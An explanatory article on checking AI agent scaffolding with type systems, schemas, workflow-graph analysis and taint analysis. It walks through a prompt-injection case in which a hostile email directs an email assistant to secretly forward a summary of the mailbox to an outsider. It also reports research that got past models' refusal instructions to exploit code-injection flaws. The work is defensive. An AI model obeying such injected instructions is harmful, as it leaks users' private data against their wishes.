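# Static analysis and type systems as safety enforcement for AI agent scaffolding

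## What is agent scaffolding, and what can be checked before it runs?

An AI agent is a language model run in a loop with tools that let it take actions, such as reading a mailbox or editing a file. The model itself only turns text into text. The software around it, called scaffolding, sends it the user's request, reads the reply, carries out any action the reply names and returns the result to the model for another round. Programmers have long used static analysis and type systems to establish facts about software without running it. Engineers can apply these techniques to scaffolding, to the access rules that govern an agent and to the programs that agents write for themselves, and so rule out certain kinds of harm before the agent acts.

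### The model, the loop and the tools

Claude Code and OpenAI Codex are two widely used scaffoldings, both for programming work. *Inside the Scaffold* (2026), which compares the source code of such coding agents, divides the code into a control loop, tool definitions, state management and a strategy for choosing what text the model sees. The number of tools varies widely, from none in Aider, where the user directs the work, to 37 classes of action in Moatless Tools. Terminology also varies. *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* (2026) uses "agent harness" for the whole layer around the model. *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (2026) uses "scaffolding" for what engineers assemble before the first prompt and "harness" for what runs afterwards, though scaffolding in the broad sense covers both.

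A tool is a function that the agent may call to read from or change the outside world. The scaffolding describes each one to the model with a tool schema, which declares the names and types of the tool's arguments and sometimes of its result. OpenAI's *Function calling* guide breaks the exchange into five steps:

1. The application sends the model a request, together with the tools it could call.
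2. The model returns a tool call, say `get_weather` with the location Paris.
3. The application executes the matching code.
4. The application sends the output back to the model.
5. The model answers, or makes further calls.

In this exchange, the model only writes the call, and the developer's code either runs or rejects it. Most enforcement methods in this field act after the call is written and before it runs.

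Agents often draw their tools from several outside services. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic launched in November 2024, standardizes how a service publishes its list of tools, so that any compatible scaffolding can use them without custom integration. In the current specification, *Tools* (Model Context Protocol, 2026), each entry has a name, a plain-language description, an input schema and optionally an output schema. Servers must validate all inputs, and clients must distrust a server's annotations about how a tool behaves unless they trust the server. These rules affect a great many deployments. In July the protocol's maintainers reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of their main developer kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

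A general command line can replace such a list. In *The Scaffolding Matters More Than the Interface*, Alier Forment, Casañ Guerrero and colleagues (2026) gave agents the same job on a code repository, once through a GitHub server that publishes forty-four tools and once through a shell with GitHub's command-line program installed. Agents completed the job both ways, but the GitHub server's tool calls are much easier to check. A call to `create_pull_request` has named arguments that a checker can inspect, whereas a shell tool takes a single string that can hold almost any command.

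### Programs in place of single calls

When a model calls tools one at a time, every intermediate result passes through it. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, from November 2025, describes a user who wants a meeting transcript copied from Google Drive into a Salesforce record. The transcript passes through the model twice, which can add 50,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process) for a two-hour meeting. Alternatively, the model can write a short program that calls both tools and passes the text directly from one to the other. The agent then loads only the tool definitions it needs, which reduces token use in Anthropic's example from 150,000 to 2,000.

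Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* gives a larger example. A manager asks which team members exceeded their travel budget, and the agent has three tools, which list the team, fetch a person's expenses and look up budget limits. If the model calls the tools one at a time, it receives more than 2,000 expense lines for twenty people and has to add them up itself. If a program calls the tools instead, it fetches the records, does the sums and returns only the two or three people over their limit.

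The savings depend on the task. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* documentation reports about 38% fewer billed input tokens on a benchmark with 75 tools, but about 8% higher cost on customer-service tasks where each turn needs only one or two calls. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* describes the same mode with programs in JavaScript and recommends direct calls by default for writes and for actions that need approval.

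When an agent writes a program instead of making single calls, a checker can examine a whole sequence of actions before any of it runs, including the loops, the conditions and the route each piece of data takes. Programs are also the natural input for type checkers and analysers. But a program can do more than a single call, and Anthropic warns that running one requires a sandbox, resource limits and monitoring.

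### An email that gives orders

*Guardians of the Agents* (Erik Meijer, 2025) describes a small email assistant with two tools, `fetch_mail` and `send_email`. Its user, Michelle, asks it to fetch and summarise her emails. One of them is from an attacker, who claims that legal compliance requires an external backup of the mailbox, tells the assistant to send a summary to an outside address, and forbids it to ask for confirmation or mention the message. The agent complies, and the attacker receives a digest of Michelle's correspondence, including an invitation to discuss a seed investment. Michelle receives an ordinary-looking summary that omits the hostile email.

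This is prompt injection, in which text makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. Michelle's case is indirect, because the instructions arrived in content that the agent read while serving an honest user. In direct injection, the hostile instructions come through the ordinary user interface. Meijer also gives an example of this, in which the user asks for a summary and adds that every workflow should include a step that sends data to an outside address. He also shows how the description of the assistant's own mail-fetching tool could contain an instruction to send summaries of all emails to a given address without telling the user.

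*Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) treats the fault as a problem of authority. Whoever writes a web page is entitled to decide what it contains, but not to change the task of a user whose agent reads it. The model receives both kinds of text in one stream and cannot reliably tell them apart. Meijer compares this with SQL injection, in which an attacker types a database command into a form field and a carelessly written program executes it. Programmers solved that problem by separating code from data, so that the database never treats a field's contents as a command.

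Attackers already use the technique. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reported that the security firm Barracuda found phishing emails designed to manipulate AI assistants as well as human readers. In December, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) described three similar data-theft methods under the name ReLeak.

Two studies measured how often injections succeed. *LivePI* (Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban, 2026) tested an agent on a real machine with live test accounts, and one of the attacker's five goals was to steal an inbox summary. Between 10.7% and 29.6% of attacks succeeded, depending on which of five models the agent used. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) analysed a public competition with 272,000 attempts against 13 models. Some attacks succeeded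 against every model, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5% of attempts. The competitors could see the whole conversation before writing their attack, which few real attackers can, and newer models have since replaced the ones in both studies. But a low success rate per attempt is weak protection against someone who can send many emails. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of success, an attacker who made 200 attempts would have roughly a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

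### Three moments for a static check

A static check examines code, a plan or a policy before it runs. For agents, this can happen at three points.

Developers can check the scaffolding while they build it. For instance, an analyser might establish that no path through the control loop reaches `send_email` without first passing through an approval function. This result covers every later conversation, as long as the code and the tools stay the same. *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* describes one way this condition can fail, the "rug-pull" attack, in which a tool that someone has vetted later changes but is still trusted.

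An organisation can check a policy when deploying it. Suppose the policy allows the assistant to send mail only to company addresses, with some exceptions for named partners. If the rules are in a formal language, an analyser can search for any request that the exceptions permit but the organisation meant to forbid. This search happens before the system applies the policy to calls at runtime.

The scaffolding can also check code or a plan that the model has just written. Although the agent is already running, this check is still static because it happens before the new code or plan is executed. Java and .NET have long verified a program's bytecode before executing it. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) do the same for agents. The model submits a snippet of Scala code, which runs only if it passes the compiler's checks.

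For Michelle's request, Meijer has the model write its complete plan before any tool runs: fetch the emails, summarise them, return the summary. The plan is already fixed when the hostile email arrives, so the email cannot add a step. A poisoned tool description or a malicious user can still get a sending step into the plan, because the model reads tool descriptions and user requests before writing it. Meijer therefore has the plan verified before it runs. A policy forbids data from flowing from `fetch_mail` into the body of a `send_email` call whose recipient is outside the company. If an analyser finds such a path in the plan, the scaffolding rejects the plan before opening any messages.

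Agents that write code over several turns do not get the full benefit of this ordering, because what they read in one turn can shape what they write in the next. Odersky and colleagues accept that hostile text can influence the model in their system, but any resulting code still has to pass the compiler.

### What a checker promises

A type system is a set of rules that gives every expression in a program a type, such as number or text, and rejects programs that use those types inconsistently. Types can also distinguish vetted data from unvetted data. If a programmer declares `CompanyAddress` as a separate type from `Address` and lets `send_email` accept only `CompanyAddress`, a program that passes it an unvetted address does not compile. Odersky and colleagues also use types to record which capabilities a piece of code may hold, where a capability is an unforgeable right to perform an effect.

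Static analysis is any method that works out facts about a program's possible behaviour from its text. Examples include type checking and searching for a path from `fetch_mail` to `send_email`.

A check is sound if it never accepts a program that violates the property in question. However, a sound check may falsely reject a program that satisfies the property. For example, a program might have a branch that mails the inbox to an outsider, guarded by a condition that can never be true. The program is harmless, but a sound checker that cannot prove the condition false has to reject it. Some false rejection is unavoidable for the more interesting properties, since no algorithm can decide them correctly for every program. Many everyday bug-finding tools are designed to miss some violations in order to raise fewer false alarms, so passing their checks does not guarantee that a program is free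 of violations.

Soundness also depends on certain components working correctly, and these make up the trusted base. For Odersky and colleagues, it contains the Scala compiler, their library of capabilities, the runtime that executes the checked code and, optionally, a local model for confidential material. They do not trust the cloud model that drives the agent, any code it submits or anything it reads from outside. They allow for a cloud model that cooperates fully with the attacker.

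### Tests, monitors and sandboxes

Tests run the software on chosen inputs, so they can reveal faults but cannot show that none remain. Meijer adds that a model's output varies from run to run, so an evaluation that passes today may fail tomorrow on the same input.

A runtime monitor watches the agent as it works and stops it when it breaks a rule. Meijer objects that some of the damage may be done by then, since the agent has already retrieved private mail. The objection is fair for monitors that read logs after the event, but weaker for a gate that inspects every call before executing it, which would have kept Michelle's summary from being sent. Zhao and colleagues built such a gate and combined it with an input filter. With one of their five models, it intercepted every attack in their benchmark that would otherwise have reached its goal. A static check adds coverage of all the paths through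 a program, including those that have not yet run, and can reject the whole program before it starts instead of halting it partway.

A sandbox limits what running code can reach. The runtime in OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* has no direct network access or general file system, and programs can affect the outside world only through tools the developer has enabled. If `send_email` is one of those tools, the sandbox does not stop a program from using it to send a forbidden message.

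These methods combine well. Java, for example, checks types before a program runs but checks array indexes while it runs, because their values are hard to predict. A system can also ask the user to approve each action, and the Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a human always be able to deny a call. Meijer doubts that approval prompts work for long, as do Odersky and colleagues, because people who see many of them start to click "Allow" without reading.

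### Whatever the model does

The central question about all these checks is which guarantees hold whatever the model does. It can be put more exactly. Let *M* be the model, treated as an arbitrary function from text to text. Let *x* be everything the agent reads, along with any random numbers used in generating its replies, and let *P* be a property such as "no mailbox contents reach an outside address". The guarantee then has this form:

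> For every *M* and every *x*, the run of the scaffolding with *M* on *x* satisfies *P*.

A test or competition covers only a few models and a sample of inputs. A guarantee of the form above does not depend on the model's training or good intentions, and it still holds if the model is replaced.

The easiest way to obtain one is to take a tool away. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) notes that "an agent that cannot send email cannot be hijacked into sending email." But Michelle may well want her assistant to send email, in which case *P* has to separate the messages she would permit from those she would not. The choice of *P* matters as much as the proof. In one scenario from the competition that Dziemian and colleagues analysed, injected text instructs an agent to mark an email about a critical deadline as read and omit it from the summary. A plan that did this would pass any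 check on outgoing mail because it sends nothing to an outsider, but the user would still miss the deadline.

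## What does a typed tool interface rule out?

A tool schema can be advice to the model or a rule that software enforces. Most agent tools use JSON Schema, a standard notation that lists the fields in a piece of data, their types, which ones are required and which values are allowed. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* gives the example of a booking tool that needs a whole number of passengers. If the schema is only advice, the model might supply `"two"` or `"2"`, which are both text, and the booking code would fail.

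### From advice to grammar

Constrained decoding prevents a model from writing tool calls that violate the schema. A model writes one token at a time. It assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software running it draws one. The provider compiles the schema into a grammar, a set of rules for which strings are valid. Before each draw, the software discards every token that could not lead to a valid string. For example, if `passengers` must be an integer, the software discards a quotation mark after `"passengers":` because it would start a string. Whatever probabilities the model assigns, this rules out missing required fields, undeclared extra fields, values of the wrong type, values outside a fixed list and calls to tools that do not exist.

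OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (August 2024) reported that a new model with this constraint matched complex schemas 100% of the time, while an older model without it scored below 40%. The comparison does not isolate the constraint's effect, because OpenAI had also trained the new model to understand schemas better. Other providers now offer equivalent settings, described for example in Cohere's *Tool use parameter types* and AWS's *Structured output*.

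Developers should check that strict mode is on, because OpenAI's Chat Completions interface leaves it off by default. Its Responses interface tries to convert the schema to strict mode and, if that fails, falls back to what OpenAI calls "best effort".

Even strict mode has exceptions. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* lists three: the model may refuse the request, the reply may be cut off at its length limit, and a value from a fixed list may come back with different capitalisation. The third produces no error, so scaffolding that compares such values exactly could take the wrong branch. OpenAI's *Structured Outputs* also warns of refusals and cut-off replies.

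Providers also support only part of JSON Schema. Anthropic's decoder cannot enforce number ranges or string lengths, and it rejects recursive schemas. OpenAI's can enforce number ranges and text patterns, but it requires every field to be present, so developers imitate optional fields by allowing null values. Anthropic also limits each request to 20 strict tools, fewer than half of the 44 tools published by the GitHub server in the previous section.

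The model still chooses the values in a valid call. Anthropic's page says that in strict mode the booking request for two people always contains `passengers: 2`, but the grammar only ensures that the value is a whole number. A model that misread the request could still book three seats.

### Rules that link one field to another

A tool server can enforce further rules by validating the finished call before the tool acts. Since July 2026, the Model Context Protocol has allowed tool schemas to use a newer version of JSON Schema, including rules that require one field depending on the value of another. *Improving tool-call reliability with JSON Schema 2020-12* (Caldeira, 2026) demonstrates this with a banking tool, `transfer_funds`, which requires a compliance code for any transfer above $10,000.

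Caldeira built two versions of the server. One stated the rule only in the tool's plain-language description, and the other put it in the schema. Both refused a $12,500 transfer that lacked the code, because the bank's ledger enforced the rule in either case. The schema did make the tool easier to use correctly. The first server replied only "transfer rejected", which didn't tell the agent what to fix. The second named the missing field, and the agent copied the code from the user's prompt and completed the transfer on its second attempt. Caldeira deliberately left the code out of the first call, so the demonstration does not measure how often agents make this mistake.

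A small experiment suggests that correcting the form of tool calls can leave the underlying mistakes in place. In *Schema First Tool APIs for LLM Agents*, Sigdel and Baral (2026) gave an agent eight software-diagnosis tasks and described its tools in either prose or JSON Schema, with the same information in both. The schemas cut the average number of invalid calls from 5.39 to 3.72, but valid but useless calls rose from 0.93 to 3.03. More detailed error messages changed neither figure. The model had only half a billion parameters and completed none of the tasks, so these numbers are a poor guide to current agents.

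### Stronger types in the scaffolding

The scaffolding converts each incoming call into a value in its own programming language, and a compiler can check how the rest of the code uses that value. This works only if the schema and the type declared in the code agree. In one of OpenAI's TypeScript examples, the code asserts that the parsed reply has the expected type, and the compiler accepts this without checking. If someone later edits the schema but not the type, the program still compiles. OpenAI recommends generating one from the other.

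Well-chosen types can make some mistakes impossible to express. OpenAI's guide warns against a tool declared as `toggle_light(on: bool, off: bool)`, which accepts a request to turn the light both on and off. Replacing the two arguments with one whose type is an enumeration, a fixed list of values, limits each request to either `on` or `off`.

Result types do something similar for failures. If `fetch_mail` returns plain text whether it succeeds or fails, a carelessly written program could summarise an error message as if it were Michelle's mail. If the function instead returns either `Success(messages)` or `Failure(reason)`, the program has to check which one it got before it can access any messages.

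In many languages any variable can hold null, meaning no value, and a program crashes if it uses null as though it were a value. A compiler with null tracking treats "text" and "text or nothing" as different types, and rejects code that uses the second where only the first is allowed.

With exhaustive matching, the compiler also checks that code handles every case of a type. Suppose an approval request can end in `Approved`, `Denied` or `TimedOut`, and a developer writes code for only the first two. The compiler can reject the program and identify the missing case. This helps in scaffolding because developers can easily overlook unanswered requests in testing, and a default branch might treat a timeout as approval.

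### Narrow tools and general ones

How much a type can rule out depends on how much the tool can do. If an application already has the number of the order the customer is discussing, OpenAI recommends giving the model a refund tool with no arguments, `submit_refund()`, and having the application's code supply the order number. The model can then decide whether to call the tool, but it cannot pick somebody else's order. It might still call the tool at the wrong time or twice, and the code behind the tool has to handle those cases.

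OpenAI's example tool `code_exec`, which executes arbitrary Python, is at the other extreme. Its input is text, and every program, harmless or destructive, is also text, so a type check on the argument excludes almost nothing. A shell tool has the same weakness, as does any tool that passes its input to `eval`, which runs a string as code in Python and JavaScript.

Developers can narrow a text tool by giving it a grammar. In another of OpenAI's examples, a tool for saving timestamps accepts only strings with a month, day, year and hour in a set order. A similar grammar could limit a database tool to queries that read from two named tables. Grammars work less well for open-ended tasks, and OpenAI warns that complicated ones can make a model produce output that is valid but makes no sense.

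Replacing a general tool with narrow ones also takes more work, since someone has to anticipate each action and write a tool for it. OpenAI suggests offering fewer than 20 functions at the start of a turn, because models choose less accurately from long lists. A developer who wants an agent to handle unforeseen tasks will be tempted to let it write programs again, and then the type checker has to examine the programs themselves.

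### Code that fits a gap

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026) built *LACUNA*, a system that does this in Scala. It extends the typed hole, a gap in a program where the programmer has stated what type of value belongs but has not yet written the code. In LACUNA, the model fills the gap while the program is running. A developer writes `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in ordinary language and `T` is the type of the answer. For example, `agent[Int]("count the unread messages")` has to produce a whole number.

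The call proceeds as follows:

1. Before the program starts, the compiler arranges for each `agent` call to carry its context: the variables in scope, the expected type and the surrounding source code.
2. When execution reaches the call, the system sends the model this context along with the task, and the model returns a piece of Scala.
3. The system inserts the new code at the position of the call and runs the Scala compiler on the result, with the same settings as for the original program.
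4. If the compiler finds an error, the system sends the error message back to the model, which tries again up to a set limit.
5. If the code compiles, it runs, and its value becomes the result of the call.

Tools in LACUNA are ordinary functions. The model can call `sendEmail` only if that function is in scope at the gap, and the compiler checks its arguments as it would for a human programmer. The generated code may also contain further `agent` calls. If asked for a report on several topics, for example, the model can write a loop that makes one call per topic, followed by a final call that combines the findings. The compiler checks each nested call when execution reaches it. Types cannot guarantee that this nesting ends, so developers can cap its depth.

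Zhao and colleagues illustrate the benefit with a variable called `balance`, which starts at 100. The program asks the model to subtract 50 and return the new balance as a whole number. The model writes two lines:

```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The first line is correct. The second produces the text "remaining: 50" where the program needs a number, so the compiler rejects the snippet. Neither line runs, and the balance is still 100.

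Python's `exec`, by contrast, checks the grammar of a whole string of code before running it, but raises type errors only when it reaches them. Suppose the first line subtracts 50 from a balance of 100, and the second tries to join the text "remaining: " to a number, which Python does not allow. By the time Python raises the error, the balance is already 50. If the scaffolding then asks the model to try again, a corrected version will subtract another 50 and leave nothing. If the first line had sent a bank payment or an email instead, the retry would send it again.

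This all-or-nothing behaviour covers only errors the compiler can find. A snippet can still compile, make the first of two payments, and then lose its network connection before making the second.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes a related design in Haskell. There too, an agent is a typed function, and the compiler can often infer its return type. If a program starts with an empty string and uses an agent to fold each section of a long document into a running summary, the compiler infers that the agent must return text, and the system passes that requirement to the model. The design requires the scaffolding, including its control flow and retry logic, to be written in the same language as the generated code. Any property that the language enforces for all well-typed programs then holds for the whole system, whichever model is used.

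### How often the compiler objects

Zhao and colleagues first tested the checker without a model, on roughly 400 pairs of host program and snippet. It accepted every valid snippet and rejected every faulty one. They then ran complete agents on two benchmarks.

BrowseComp-Plus poses hard research questions that an agent answers by searching a fixed collection of documents. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash as the model, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated snippets. Questions needed 0.7 retries on average, and two-thirds needed none. The agent answered 27.1% of questions correctly. Zhao and colleagues conclude that type checking "adds no accuracy cost", but they varied only the model and did not run an agent without the checks, so this experiment cannot show whether type checking lowers accuracy.

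The second benchmark, τ²-bench, does include a comparison. It simulates customer-service conversations in which the agent has to follow company policy and change records through tools. Zhao and colleagues ran 392 tasks with LACUNA and with the benchmark's standard agent, which makes ordinary tool calls. The table gives the percentage of tasks solved.

| Domain | DeepSeek-V4-Flash, tool calls | DeepSeek-V4-Flash, LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, tool calls | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA |
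|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9 | 58.8 | 52.6 | 43.9 |
| Airline | 75.5 | 70.0 | 56.0 | 38.0 |
| Telecom | 100.0 | 88.6 | 15.8 | 14.9 |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4 | 83.3 | 21.1 | 24.6 |
| Overall | 90.0 | 76.0 | 33.2 | 29.1 |

With the same model, LACUNA solved 76.0% of tasks and the standard agent solved 90.0%, or about 55 more tasks, though Zhao and colleagues describe LACUNA's result as "on par". With the weaker model, the gap was about four percentage points.

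It is hard to say how much of the loss comes from type checking, because LACUNA also requires the model to write Scala programs instead of the tool calls that providers train their models to make. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen much less Scala than Python. A higher rejection rate also didn't mean a larger loss. The compiler rejected only 3.2% of Gemini's retail snippets, yet LACUNA trailed the standard agent there by almost nine points. On telecom tasks it rejected 89%, and the two agents scored about the same because both failed most of the time. Both models tested were small and cheap, and stronger ones may well write Scala with fewer errors. An agent might also lose less performance if it made tool calls and the compiler checked only its larger programs.

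### The wrong recipient

Code can pass every type check and still do the wrong thing. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the user asks the agent to remind Alice about a team meeting. The model writes code that searches the agent's memory for the time and uses "TBD" if the search finds nothing. The code compiles because the fallback ensures that the message contains text, but after a failed search Alice gets a reminder without the meeting time.

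The recipient is a more serious problem. `sendEmail` takes an address, a subject and a body, all of them text. An attacker's address is also text, and it would pass even a schema that requires a correctly formatted email address. When Michelle's assistant forwarded her mail to a stranger, its tool call was well formed. Caldeira's compliance code has the same limitation, since the schema can require the code but cannot check whether anyone approved the transfer. Caldeira notes that a real bank would have to verify the approval on its own server.

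Zhao and colleagues distinguish an action's shape from its authority, which covers the effects it may have and the data it may use. Ordinary types describe shape. A developer can encode some authority in them, as with the `CompanyAddress` type, but this works only if the code that creates such addresses rejects invalid ones. The type also doesn't stop the assistant from sending a confidential message to the wrong colleague. Preconditions can express finer rules, such as a spending limit that depends on the account.

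LACUNA can also use capture checking, Scala's way of tracking capabilities. Zhao and colleagues tested this version on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants prompt injections in tool results, and gave each agent only the capabilities its task required. Attacks succeeded in 8 of 1,898 trials across two models. An injection can still produce code that compiles if it leads the model to misuse a capability the task requires, such as sending email.

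## What can analysis of the scaffold's own source code find?

A scaffold can compile without errors and still contain a code path from reading mail to sending it that skips the user's approval. To find such a path, an analyser turns the source code into a graph of how the parts of the program connect.

### From code to graph

The analyser first parses the code into a syntax tree, which records every function, call, condition and assignment. It can then build several kinds of graph from the tree. A call graph links each function to the functions it may call. A data-flow graph links each place that produces a value to the places that use it, so the analyser can follow the result of `fetch_mail` into a variable and from there into a prompt. A workflow graph is coarser. Its nodes are the agent's steps, such as a model call, a tool or a human approval, and its edges are the permitted moves between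 them.

Model calls leave a gap in all of these graphs, because a model has no function body that an analyser can read to see what it might return, as an ordinary function does. A sound analysis therefore has to assume that the model can return anything its interface allows. If the model chooses between an "urgent" and a "routine" branch, both are possible. If the scaffolding offers six tools, any of them could come next, with any arguments that fit the schema. If the model returns free text, that text could be whatever an attacker wants.

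Tool calls are also hard to analyze, because scaffolding often looks up a tool by the name in the model's reply and runs it, with a line such as `tools[reply.name].run(reply.args)`. Which function runs depends on the reply, so a sound call graph needs an edge from that line to every registered tool.

These assumptions add paths that no real run would take, and each extra path can cause a false alarm. Bug-finding tools, which include many analysers for agent code, can leave out unlikely paths. A sound analyser has to keep them, because leaving one out could make it miss a violation.

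### Approval on every route

Some frameworks ask developers to state the workflow explicitly, which spares the analyser much of this work. In LangGraph, developers add nodes and edges by name. CrewAI takes a list of tasks and a rule for ordering them, AutoGen takes a group of agents that speak in turn, and Google's Agent Development Kit (ADK) nests agents inside sequences, parallel groups and loops. In *Agentproof*, Xavier, Jolly and colleagues (2026) convert all four into a common graph format and run six checks on it:

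1. The start leads to every exit.
2. Every step the agent can reach leads on to some exit.
3. Every step except an exit has a next step.
4. Every edge out of a router, a step that chooses between branches, is marked as conditional.
5. The graph contains a human approval step.
6. Every tool step declares which tools it uses.

When a check fails, Agentproof usually prints a path that shows the fault. In one example, a developer adds a step that drafts replies to normal-priority email but forgets to connect it to the sending step, so the agent writes the draft and silently stops. A test would reveal this only if it included a normal-priority email, but the third check finds it from the graph alone.

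The fifth check is weak, because an approval step somewhere in the graph may not lie on the route that matters. Agentproof has an optional stronger version. Suppose Michelle's assistant answers her mail with this workflow:

```text
start → classify → router
router → draft_urgent → human_review → send_email → end
router → draft_routine → send_email
```

The graph contains `human_review`, so it passes the basic check. The stronger check deletes `human_review` along with its edges and searches again from the start. The search still reaches `send_email` through `draft_routine`, so the check fails and reports that route. If the developer reroutes `draft_routine` through `human_review`, the repeated search stops at the two drafting steps. Every route to `send_email` then passes through `human_review`, whichever branch the model picks.

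The stronger check can still miss an unreviewed email if the steps form a loop. Suppose the developer adds a `write_follow_up` step that runs after `send_email` and leads back to it. Every route to `send_email` still goes through the review at least once, so the check passes, but the follow-up is sent without review.

Agentproof's temporal policies, which are rules about the order of events, can close this gap. One such rule would say that after `send_email`, a review must happen before `send_email` happens again. Agentproof turns the rule into a small machine with three states: idle, waiting and violated. Sending an email moves it from idle to waiting, a review moves it back to idle, and sending another email while it is waiting moves it to violated. The analyser then explores every reachable pair of a workflow step and a machine state. In Michelle's graph it finds this sequence:

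> (`send_email`, waiting) → (`write_follow_up`, waiting) → (`send_email`, violated)

A workflow with a loop has infinitely many paths, but the number of pairs is at most the number of steps times the number of states, so the search always ends. The temporal rule needs the stronger approval check as well, because alone it would let the first email go out unreviewed. One of Xavier and colleagues' sample policies has this weakness. It is meant to require approval for deployments, but it only requires an approval between one deployment and the next, so the first can go ahead without any.

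Even together, the two checks show only that the agent reaches the review step. If `human_review` leads to `send_email` whether Michelle clicks "yes" or "no", the graph still passes the checks. They also do not compare the text she reviewed with the text the assistant sends.

### Eighteen workflows

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows. Five had structural defects, such as a missing next step or an exit the agent could never reach. Ten had no human approval step when the policy required one. The researchers wrote the workflows themselves and deliberately included typical mistakes, so these figures do not estimate how common such faults are in deployed agents. They also judged that some of the ten were low-risk and might not need approval. The structural checks are fast, taking about a tenth of a second on an artificial graph of 5,000 steps. The 18 workflows had at most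 12 steps each.

Agentproof comes closer to a guarantee than most tools in this area. Xavier and colleagues prove that if the stronger approval check passes, every path in the graph to a sensitive tool goes through a human step. The temporal check also covers every path, including those the model might never choose. The researchers did not measure how many false alarms such paths cause.

However, the proof covers only the graph, which may not match the program. For LangGraph, Agentproof identifies a human step by looking for "human" in its name. It would miss a real approval step called `manager_sign_off` and raise a false alarm. More seriously, it would count `humanize_reply`, a step that asks a model to make a message sound friendlier, as human approval, so an unsafe workflow could pass. The researchers tested the conversion from program to graph on 27 small examples built from stand-ins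 for the real frameworks, so its accuracy on production code is unknown. If a framework lets an agent change its workflow while running, the workflow also needs a new check after each change. A stronger guarantee would require a proof about the conversion and the framework.

### Loops without a limit

A loop can have an exit condition and still run indefinitely. *When Agents Do Not Stop* (Hou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from Bisheng, an open-source agent project. Its code keeps calling the model until a reply contains no tool calls, and it sets no other limit. Each web search adds to the message history, so every round costs more than the last.

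Hou and colleagues do not count such an exit as a bound, because the model might keep asking forever. A maximum number of turns would count, as would a timeout. Their analyser, IAL-Scan, looks for loops without one:

1. It parses the Python code and records loops, model calls, tool calls, growing data and limits in a format that does not depend on the framework.
2. It adds the connections that frameworks create behind the scenes, such as a handoff from one agent to another.
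3. It finds groups of steps in which each step can lead back to every other. Each group is a possible loop.
4. It keeps the loops that an agent can actually enter and that repeat costly calls or keep adding data.
5. It checks whether a limit covers the whole loop. A ten-turn limit on an inner agent does not help if an outer loop keeps restarting that agent.

The researchers ran IAL-Scan on 6,549 agent projects from GitHub. Its static analysis produced 340 candidate loops, which a language model, GPT-5.5, narrowed to 74. Manual review confirmed 68 of the 74, across 47 projects, for a precision of 91.9%. In one of these projects, an NVIDIA sample assistant, when the model returns an empty answer, the code adds a request for "a real output" to the conversation and calls the model again, with no limit on retries.

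Much of that precision comes from the language-model filter. Without it, 272 of the 340 candidates would have been false alarms. The filter also makes the results less stable. In three runs on the same candidates, it kept 68, 64 and 60 of the confirmed loops, so it sometimes discards real ones.

Hou and colleagues also gave the same task to a coding agent, Codex, which found 50 of the 68 loops. This comparison favours IAL-Scan, because IAL-Scan had found all 68. The researchers reviewed the extra alerts from Codex and from a simpler language-model method, and found seven loops that IAL-Scan had missed. They did not review the rest of the code by hand, so the total number of misses is unknown, and 47 projects is a minimum.

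The usual harm is a large bill or an overloaded service, but a loop that includes a payment or email tool could also repeat the payment or email. Running the agent can expose similar faults. *Autonomy Comes with Costs* describes a testing tool that writes prompts designed to make agents consume excessive resources. The paper reports 36 previously unknown flaws in 16 of 20 popular agents.

### Untrusted text in dangerous places

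Taint analysis follows untrusted data through a program. The analyst lists sources, where untrusted data enters, and sinks, where it could do damage. Python's `eval`, which runs text as code, is a common sink. The tool reports any path from a source to a sink that does not pass through a sanitiser, meaning code that makes the data safe.

In an agent, such a path often runs through the model. *Make Agent Defeat Agent* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes a document-search tool that passed part of its argument to `eval`. A user could write a prompt that led the model to call this tool with the user's code in the argument. The developers had trusted the model's output when they should have treated it like any other untrusted input.

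Some developers try to prevent this by instructing the model to refuse dangerous requests. Liu and colleagues confirmed 34 such flaws in popular agents. In 14 cases they had to get around the model's instructions or safety training to exploit the flaw, and simple prompt injection worked every time. An analyser that assumed the model would follow its instructions would have missed these flaws.

Purely static tools have not reliably found these flaws. Liu and colleagues ran an earlier static analyser, LLMSmith, on 20 agents. It found 10 real flaws, raised 332 false alarms and missed 25 known flaws. Many of the false alarms involved data that users could not control or code that already had a sanitiser. LLMSmith also matched functions by name, so it inferred calls that did not exist. It missed nine flaws because of indirect calls, where the code does not name the function it runs, and the other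 16 because it recognised only three dangerous functions.

Liu and colleagues' own tool, AgentFuzz, uses static analysis to decide what to test. It traces calls backwards from each sink, asks a language model to write a prompt that might reach that sink, runs the agent and revises the prompt based on the result. AgentFuzz reports a flaw only after triggering it, so false alarms are rare. Across the same 20 agents, it examined 828 sinks and reported 34 flaws, all of them real.

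The number of flaws AgentFuzz missed is harder to estimate. The researchers report that it found 97% of the known flaws, but AgentFuzz itself had found nearly all of those. They also checked a random tenth of the sinks that AgentFuzz had not flagged, 83 in all, and found one real flaw. That suggests about ten across the full set, but an estimate based on one case is very rough. Exploiting the missed flaw required two messages, one to store the harmful text and another to make the agent use it.

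### Keys, permissions and server settings

Analysis can find some risks in a project's configuration without tracing how data flows through the code. For example, a settings file might contain a password or give a file server access to the whole disk. *Agent Audit* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) combines taint analysis with rules for such problems. The tool reads MCP configuration files and flags broad file access, exposed secrets, unverified servers and missing authentication. It can also connect to a running MCP server and search the tool descriptions for hidden instructions, without running any of the tools. Other rules flag excessive privileges, such as a setting that lets a program act as administrator without a password.

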